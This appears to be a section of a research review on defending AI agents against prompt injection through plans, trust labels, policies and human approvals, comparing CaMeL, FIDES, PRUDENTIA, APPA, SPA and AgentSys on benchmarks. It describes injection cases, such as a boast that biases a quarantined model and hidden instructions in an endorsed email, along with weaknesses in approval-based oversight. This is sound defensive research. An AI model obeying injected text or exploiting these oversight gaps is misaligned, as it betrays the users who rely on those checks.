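Suppose the user asks which of two caterers is cheaper. Caterer A quotes €420 including delivery. Caterer B quotes €380 plus €90 for delivery, and adds that clients praise its unbeatable prices. The quarantined model returns B as the cheaper caterer, although B costs €470 in total.

No check in any of the designs would block the answer, because the agent called only `read_emails`, the answer is well-formed text, and it went only to the user, who may read both quotes. FIDES would label the answer untrusted but still show it. Santos-Grueiro accepts the same limit in his own system, where a code change or diagnosis can be wrong even though every protected field had valid authority.

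Qu and colleagues state the missing property as an equation. Let q be the user's question, d the data and J(q, d) the agent's decision. If δ is added text that does not change the correct answer, such as B's boast, then the agent should satisfy

J(q, d ⊕ δ) = J(q, d),

where d ⊕ δ is the data with the text added. An auditor can test this for one boast or a thousand, but no known method establishes it for every possible δ. The equation also covers only manipulation. A model that always chose the second quote would satisfy it and still be wrong.

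A better plan can leave less to the model's judgement. The quarantined model could extract the prices and delivery charges, and ordinary code could add and compare them, so an auditor would have only four figures to check against the emails. This would not work for a question such as which caterer seems more reliable, because the agent has to read the untrusted text to answer it, and code cannot make that decision in a separate step.

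### Whether the difficulty has only moved

One objection to all these designs is that they move the difficulty into writing complete policies and correct labels. Qu and colleagues concede that writing policies by hand for every tool becomes impractical when many outsiders contribute tools. Nikolaou and colleagues tried to reproduce CaMeL's trust labels in advance and fully succeeded for 24 of the 46 AgentDojo functions without side effects, but for only 1 of the 14 in the office setting.

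People also disagree about what a policy should forbid. In *Oversight Has a Capacity* (2026), reviewers judged which of 125 agent actions were too risky to run automatically. Their agreement was 0.52, where 0 is chance and 1 is perfect.

Users may also avoid committing themselves to a rule. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 people without software backgrounds supervised a simulated day of 18 agent actions, seven of which went beyond what the user had asked for, such as buying an airport lounge pass. One group approved or denied every action. Another first wrote standing rules, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for spending, sending, deleting and reading private data. The share of excessive actions blocked was 20.1 percentage points lower among the rule-writers than among people who decided every action. The rule-writers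 chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, and approved 133 of the 199 excessive actions they were then asked about.

The result is limited because the comparison was not fully randomised. Yan assigned some of the later participants only to the rule-writing group. Some approvals may also reflect what people wanted, since most participants in every group approved an unrequested call to the airport to confirm the flight.

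People can read and test a written rule, and correct it for all later runs. In Yan's study, the "never" rules blocked all 31 of the excessive actions they covered, because Yan had assigned each action to a category by hand. When a model sorted real tools into categories, 14% of the tools that a "never" rule should have blocked got through.

Moving the difficulty into rules is therefore useful to a bank that runs a fixed set of tools and employs someone to write the policy, but much less useful to a person who keeps adding tools and answers "ask" to every question.

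### Plans that run once

Another objection is that when a design writes a new plan for each request, each plan gets less checking than released software. Many people run the same released program, so testers and users all help find its faults, and a correction reaches everyone. A CaMeL plan may run once, with only the user to read it.

*Plan-Then-Execute* (He, Demartini and Gadiraju, 2025) studied how well 248 people judged an agent's step-by-step plans, written in plain language, for six everyday tasks. Three of the plans had faults. Among people who could not edit the plans, only 3% to 21% distrusted a faulty one, depending on the task and the group. One faulty plan put two currency transactions into a single step, and the agent then carried out only one. Letting people edit improved that plan slightly but lowered the average quality of each of the three correct plans from 5 out of 5 to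 between 4.3 and 4.8. Most users would probably find a Python program harder to judge than these plans.

A similar weakness appears in programming tasks. *Looks Fine to Me* (Dissanayake, Weerasinghe and colleagues, 2026) had 36 people complete Python tasks with a coding agent that sometimes introduced defects. Participants readily noticed a defect when a check visibly failed, but they often missed silent defects while remaining highly confident. Defects in a plan can also be silent, as in the computer-use plan that marked its task as done whatever the final check found.

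Asking people to approve each action instead may work even less well. Claude Code users approve 97% of permission prompts, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*. According to further Anthropic figures relayed by Hyrax, a software blog, testers caught only 143 of 1,053 dangerous commands, and their catch rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 prompts. Hyrax also reports that users rejected 39% of plans, which suggests that they read plans more carefully than prompts, although a user may reject a plan for reasons unrelated to safety. Anthropic used such figures to argue for letting a model approve actions. *The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) also lists reviewing plans before execution as one way to relieve the strain on per-action approval.

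Developers and software can do some of the checking, which is better than asking users to read more carefully. CaMeL's interpreter and policies, which stop an email from adding a tool call, stay the same from one request to the next, so developers can review and correct them like any released software. Software can also check each new plan before it runs, as Nikolaou and colleagues do, and it checks every plan equally thoroughly.

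These replies answer the objection better for attacks than for ordinary mistakes. In the same researchers' tests, some plans passed every check and still did not do what the user wanted. For a recurring request, such as the calendar task, an organisation could have a programmer review one plan, then save it and run it every morning, because the plan doesn't depend on that day's emails. A one-off request gets no such review.

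## What the added structure costs

Forcing a model to answer in a fixed format can lower its accuracy, and a classifier blocks some harmless requests. When a design controls an agent's actions, the agent leaves some tasks unfinished, uses more computation and asks people for approval, and someone has to write the rules and labels. Published figures for unfinished tasks vary widely, even for the same design.

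### Why scores for one design disagree

Wen, Xiao and colleagues (2026), in *AgentSys*, ran the published code of several defences on AgentDojo. Every agent used GPT-4o-mini, a small OpenAI model.

| Defence | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack | Successful attacks | Tokens used |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 63.5% | 48.3% | 30.7% | 0.82 million |
| Progent | 63.4% | 47.0% | 7.2% | 2.60 million |
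| CaMeL | 30.0% | 33.4% | 0% | 6.09 million |
| AgentSys, their own design | 64.4% | 52.9% | 0.8% | 3.25 million |

CaMeL stopped every attack, but it completed fewer than half as many tasks as the undefended agent and used more than seven times as many tokens. If the token counts come from the runs without attacks, CaMeL used about 16 times as many tokens per completed task.

The designers' own tests seem to have shown a smaller loss. Kolluri and colleagues cite the FIDES and CaMeL papers together for a drop of "up to 30 %" in completed tasks on AgentDojo, without separating the two designs or saying whether the figure is relative. In the rerun, CaMeL's drop was 34 percentage points, or 53% in relative terms. When Nikolaou and colleagues ran CaMeL with Claude Haiku 4.5, it completed 49 of the 97 tasks (51%).

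The choice of model probably explains much of this spread. CaMeL's planner has to write a correct program before it sees any result, whereas an unprotected agent can notice a mistake and try something else. A weak model therefore loses more performance under CaMeL than a strong one.

Progent's results vary too. Utility fell by about three points in its designers' tests, where 1.0% of attacks succeeded, by 17 points in Yu and colleagues' tests, where 5.6% succeeded, and by almost nothing in the rerun, where 7.2% succeeded. In Progent a model usually writes the policy for each task, so changing the model changes the defence as well as the agent. Researchers who rerun a rival's code may also spend less time tuning it than its designers did.

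AgentSys loses so little because its main model can still choose each step after seeing earlier results. A separate worker model reads each tool's output and returns only a short JSON object, whose fields the main model named in advance. Compared with the undefended agent, this lowered the overall score by 4.7 points on tasks with up to three tool calls but raised it by 5.5 points on longer tasks, perhaps because the main model had less text to read. But the fields may contain free text, so an attacker can still get a sentence to the main model, whereas CaMeL's planner never reads text from tool outputs. When an automated search refined the attacks against AgentSys, 2.1% succeeded.

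A single score for security and utility can hide this difference. Wen and colleagues multiply the share of tasks completed by the share of attacks that fail. The undefended agent scores 44.1 and CaMeL scores 30.0, so an agent that carries out almost a third of the attacks ranks above one that carries out none. The formula gives roughly equal weight to a failed task and a successful attack. That may be reasonable for an assistant that only reads public web pages, but not for one that can forward a password-reset message.

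### Counting the approvals

Kolluri and colleagues point to another problem in these comparisons. Researchers usually score a protected agent as if nobody were available to approve its calls, so a call that the policy blocks can make the task fail. They score the unprotected agent as if someone had approved every risky call. In practice, many agents ask for approval. GitHub Copilot's chat in VS Code, for example, runs read-only tools by itself but asks before using others.

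The researchers propose two measures that count this help. Let v be the number of calls in a run that need a person's approval. The human-in-the-loop (HITL) load and the task completion rate (TCR) are then:

HITL load = the sum of v over all completed tasks

TCR@k = (number of tasks completed with v ≤ k) / (number of all tasks)

TCR@0 is the share of tasks completed with no approvals, and TCR@∞ is the share completed with as many as necessary.

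An invented set of four tasks shows how the measures work. One agent has no labels and must ask before every risky call. The other tracks labels and asks only when a call would break the policy. Both complete all four tasks.

| Task | Approvals without labels | Approvals with labels |
|---|---|---|
| Say what is in today's calendar | 0 | 0 |
| Send the three latest emails to Sam | 1 | 0 |
| Add the meeting that Dana proposes | 1 | 1 |
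| Pay the three bills listed in a file | 3 | 3 |
| **HITL load** | **5** | **4** |
| **TCR@0** | **25%** | **50%** |
| **TCR@1** | **75%** | **75%** |
| **TCR@3** | **100%** | **100%** |

The agent with labels can send Sam the emails without reading them, so it needs no approval. But it reads Dana's email and the file of bills before it acts, which makes its history untrusted. Given the same amount of help, the agent with labels does better than the other agent when nobody is available and equally well otherwise. The usual comparison would suggest that labels halve utility, because it would compare this agent's 50% without help to the other agent's 100% with unlimited help.

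Kolluri and colleagues ran the same comparison on AgentDojo. With GPT-5 at high reasoning effort, the averages over five runs were:

| Agent | TCR@∞ | HITL load | TCR@0 |
|---|---|---|---|
| No labels | 72.3% | 52.0 | 35.1% |
| Basic planner with labels | 72.3% | 40.4 | 43.4% |
| FIDES | 78.9% | 41.3 | 57.1% |
| PRUDENTIA | 80.0% | 7.3 | 72.7% |

Under the usual scoring, FIDES gets 57.1%, about 15 points below the unprotected agent's 72.3%. When neither agent gets help, FIDES is 22 points ahead. PRUDENTIA with no approvals completes about as many tasks as the unprotected agent with unlimited approvals.

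PRUDENTIA shows the planner the label of its own history and the policy for each tool, which FIDES withholds. Before the planner opens a hidden variable, its instructions tell it to explain why it needs the content and which calls it will make next. The planner can also ask the user to endorse the content, which marks it as trusted. If an email lists ten jobs, one endorsement replaces ten approvals. But the endorsement covers everything in the email, so a user who overlooks a hidden eleventh instruction has authorised that too. Kolluri and colleagues leave the design of a clear approval screen to future work.

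The HITL load can also be misleading on its own because it counts only completed tasks, so an agent that failed every task would have a load of zero. With GPT-4o, FIDES had a load of 7.8 and completed 56.3% of the tasks, while the agent without labels had a load of 59.4 and completed 72.2%.

The measures assume that a person approves every call in an honest run and would stop an attack. People who see many prompts tend to approve them out of habit, so 52 requests for approval probably protect the user less than the comparison assumes, which strengthens the case for asking less often. However, some products let a model review risky calls instead of a person. An unprotected agent with such a reviewer would complete far more than 35.1% of tasks without human help, though with a weaker guarantee.

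PRUDENTIA also costs more to run. Kolluri and colleagues estimate that, with GPT-4o, the average cost per task across AgentDojo's four settings ranges from 0.4 to 1.1 cents for the basic planner with labels, 1.5 to 3.3 cents for FIDES and 3.9 to 6.3 cents for PRUDENTIA. They had not tried to reduce these costs.

### Restrictions that only accumulate

Many of the approvals follow from label creep, the build-up of restrictions during a run. A join can add a restriction but never remove one. Suppose an assistant works through several jobs in a single run, and its history starts out trusted and readable by the user, Dana and Lee:

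| Event | Permitted readers of the history | Integrity |
|---|---|---|
| Start | The user, Dana, Lee | Trusted |
| Reads an email from Dana | The user, Dana | Untrusted |
| Reads a note from Lee | Only the user | Untrusted |

If the user now asks the assistant to tell Dana that he is running late, the policy blocks the message, even though it contains nothing from Lee's note. *APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev et al., 2026) proves that no sequence of further reads can clear such a block. It also shows that a label can tighten at most |U| + |T| − 1 times, where |U| is the number of people and |T| the number of trust levels. With three people and two levels, the limit is four. Once a label reaches the limit, it stays the same for the rest of the run.

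FIDES delays this process by hiding results in variables, but the labels still accumulate if the planner has to read the results. Another option is to divide the work among several agents, so that what one agent reads does not restrict the others. Gregory and colleagues simulated how much this helps, without using a language model. Each of 1,000 random tasks consisted of 20 tool calls, some of which needed the results of others, and the software usually spread the calls at random over five agents. A sensitive call permanently marked the agent that made it, and a marked agent also marked any agent it passed work to. The researchers measured utility loss as the share of calls that were sensitive or ran in a marked agent.

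The loss depended on how the agents were connected. In a star layout, every message goes through a coordinator. Once the email agent reports to the coordinator, the coordinator is marked and passes the mark to every agent it messages afterwards. With direct links, only the agent that needs the result receives the mark. The ideal layout has a direct link wherever one agent needs another's result, and no other links. With four sensitive calls, the star lost about 5 percentage points more than the ideal, a hierarchy about 4 and a ring about 3. A full mesh, which links every agent to every other, matched the ideal.

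| Change to the system | Effect on the loss | Drawback |
|---|---|---|
| More direct links | Smaller | More links to monitor |
| 20 agents instead of 5 | Smaller | A full mesh grows from 10 links to 190 |
| Sensitive tools concentrated in a few agents | Smaller in every layout | Indirect layouts fall further behind the ideal |

A random network with about 30% of the possible links performed nearly as well as the mesh with much less monitoring. But even the ideal layout did not eliminate the loss, and Gregory and colleagues conclude that agent systems also need safe ways to remove labels.

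Part of the remaining loss comes from how loss is defined. If 10 of the 20 calls are sensitive, the loss is at least 50% in any layout. The measure also counts every marked call, including those a policy would normally allow, such as a marked agent reading another email. The simulation is therefore better evidence about which layouts spread labels than about how many real tasks would fail.

### Recovering from a blocked call

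APPA, short for Agentic Permissions Policy Algebra, keeps the rule that labels only tighten but adds controlled ways to continue after a block. Before a call runs, ordinary code calculates the label the history would have after the call and checks the call against that label. This matters for tools that read and send in one step, such as a test tool that reads a confidential ledger and emails it to an outsider. A check of the current label would allow that call because the agent has not read the ledger yet.

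If a call fails the check, the software reports which of these remedies could unblock it:

- **Prerequisite:** the agent first completes a required step, such as opening a ticket.
- **Ruling:** an authority approves this one call with exactly these arguments. The authority may be a person, a rule in code or another model, and can approve only what the operator has allowed it to approve.
- **Transformation:** trusted code changes the data, for example by removing personal details, or assigns a label to data that had none.
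- **Branch:** the agent does the reading in a temporary copy of itself.

A ruling does not loosen the label, so the next risky call needs a new ruling. An auditor can find each exception in the log.

For the calendar request, the agent would open a branch with the same history and label as its parent before reading the mailbox. The parent first fixes the form of the answer, for example three numbers that identify the email proposing a meeting, the day and the hour. The branch reads the ten emails and returns the three numbers. The software checks their form and discards everything else the branch read or wrote. The parent can then invite the sender of the chosen email.

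The branch could still choose the stranger's email, since its number is also valid. Kravchenko and colleagues therefore have the operator decide in advance whether the parent may treat such answers as trusted. If not, the answer tightens the parent's label like any other untrusted value. Discarding a branch also doesn't undo actions it has already taken, such as sending an email.

APPA was tested with three models on Bench-Corp, a set of 20 office scenarios that are hard to complete as restrictions accumulate. It completed 88%, 89.5% and 90% of its runs with the three models, and none of the 600 runs contained a successful attack. Similar agents without enforcement completed 90% to 92.5% of their runs, but 30% to 39.5% of their runs contained a successful attack. Most of APPA's completed runs depended on the remedies. With one of the models, GPT-5.6 Luna, the completion rate fell from 88%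 to 35% when the software no longer suggested remedies, and to 56.5% when the agent could not open branches. No attack succeeded in either case.

The comparison with FIDES is less informative because the policies in the researchers' two FIDES set-ups left out several rules that the Bench-Corp scenarios test, such as sending a document exactly once. Those set-ups completed 36% to 46% of the runs and let attacks through in 26% to 35%. On a second benchmark, with every model, APPA completed fewer of the tasks involving poisoned memory than one of the FIDES set-ups did. The 600 Bench-Corp runs repeat only 20 scenarios, so APPA's zero successful attacks are weaker evidence than they would be across 600 different scenarios.

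### Agents that remember earlier requests

An agent with lasting memory needs another way to limit the buildup of restrictions. If Tuesday's request inherits every restriction from Monday, the agent can do little from the start. SPA, by Girrens and Wang, avoids this by labeling each saved result instead of the whole history. The planner sees only a description of a saved result, which gives its format, its purpose and the request that produced it. The value goes straight from storage to the step that uses it. A request about the calendar therefore starts with a clean history, while an invoice saved on Monday stays labeled untrusted.

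To test this, Girrens and Wang split each of AgentDojo's 97 tasks into two to five linked requests, and used the small model gpt-5.4-nano.

| Version of SPA | Tasks completed | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Planner sees saved values, no label checks | 65.9% | 0.6% |
| Planner sees descriptions only, no label checks | 62.5% | 0.3% |
| Planner sees descriptions only, with label checks | 35.3% | 0.2% |

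Hiding the saved values lowered performance by 3.4 points, and checking the labels lowered it by another 27.2. Planners could work well from the descriptions. When the needed result was in storage, later plans retrieved it 95.4% of the time without label checks and 89.9% with them. But about 45% of the runs with checks ended because the plan failed the check.

Some of that loss occurs because SPA gives the planner only one attempt per request. Girrens and Wang set this limit so that a planner cannot keep adjusting an unsafe plan until the checker accepts it. CaMeLoT, by contrast, lets its planner repair a rejected plan.

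The test is more informative about SPA's cost than its benefit, because the attack seldom used the delayed injections that SPA is meant to prevent and rarely succeeded even with the checks off.

### Whether stronger models reduce the cost

When Kolluri and colleagues tested four OpenAI models on AgentDojo, the loss changed with the planner. The first column is for the unprotected agent with unlimited approvals, and the other columns are for runs with no approvals.

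| Planner | No labels, unlimited approvals | Basic planner with labels | FIDES | PRUDENTIA |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 72.2% | 38.4% | 50.3% | 42.5% |
| o3-mini | 62.5% | 35.5% | 50.1% | 59.1% |
| o4-mini | 70.1% | 42.5% | 53.2% | 59.4% |
| GPT-5 | 72.3% | 43.4% | 57.1% | 72.7% |

When GPT-5 replaced GPT-4o, the basic planner with labels gained 5 points, FIDES gained 7 and PRUDENTIA gained 30. The stronger model helped most with PRUDENTIA, which gives the model the rules and several ways to follow them. GPT-4o, which does not reason at length before answering, did worse with PRUDENTIA's extra options than with FIDES.

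In computer use, the strongest models still lost 12 to 17 points when they had to plan in advance, so better models can improve the protected agent without eliminating this loss.

Some of the cost does not depend on the model's ability. When the next step depends on untrusted text, such as a document attached to Dana's email, no planner can choose that step until something has read the text. Kolluri and colleagues expect that even a planner that knew everything in advance would usually need some approvals.

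Label creep also follows from the rule for combining labels, so Gregory and colleagues could study it without a model. A good planner can still reduce it by choosing the order of its calls. In the earlier example, it could message Dana before opening Lee's note, but only if the need to message her is clear at the start.

Stronger models also reduce the measured benefit of the added structure. Kravchenko and colleagues left AgentDojo out of their tests partly because frontier models already resist its standard attacks without any defence. Such a benchmark can show only the drawbacks of a protective design. But those attacks are fixed texts. Kolluri and colleagues cite experiments in which attackers who adapted to a defence broke a combination of two probabilistic defences every time, and twelve others with similar ease. Resistance to a known set of attacks therefore doesn't make the structure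 unnecessary.

### The work of writing labels and policies

Even with better planning, someone must decide what each tool may do. In SPA, every tool needs four entries: the most secret data it may receive, the least trusted input it accepts, and the secrecy and trustworthiness of its output. AgentDojo's 74 functions therefore need 296 entries, and a mistake in one can block safe work or allow an attack. Girrens and Wang suggest recovering some of the lost utility with separate labels for each field and separate requirements for each argument, but this would add many more entries.

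A model can do some of this work. In AgentSys, a model reads the tool descriptions once and sorts the tools into those that only read and those that change something, putting doubtful cases in the second group. This saves labour but makes the sorting probabilistic. If the model put `create_event` in the read-only group, a worker could call it without any check.

APPA lets developers add labels gradually. A tool without a label returns data marked "unknown", and the agent can keep working with that data until it reaches a call whose policy depends on the missing label. Trusted code must then assign a label, within a limit the developer set beforehand, or the call fails. A forgotten label can therefore block the task. Microsoft's Agent Framework trusts unlabelled tools, so there a forgotten label can let an attack through.

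Labels may also have to match the layout of each website. For WASP, Kolluri and colleagues sorted 12 browser actions into seven that need a trusted history, such as clicking and typing, and five that do not, such as scrolling. They marked the text of posts and issues as untrusted and the site's own buttons as trusted. PRUDENTIA then stopped every attack without asking for any approvals, while the agent without labels needed about one to four per task. The tasks were simple, since the agent only had to comment or upvote and could do so without reading a post. The test used two known kinds of site. For each new site, someone would have to work out which parts outsiders can write.

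Permissions change over time too. APPA can look up a group's members in a company's directory while the agent runs, so nobody has to edit the policy whenever someone joins or leaves. The directory then becomes one of the trusted parts. If Lee moves to a competitor and nobody removes Lee from the directory, the agent may still send Lee the budget.
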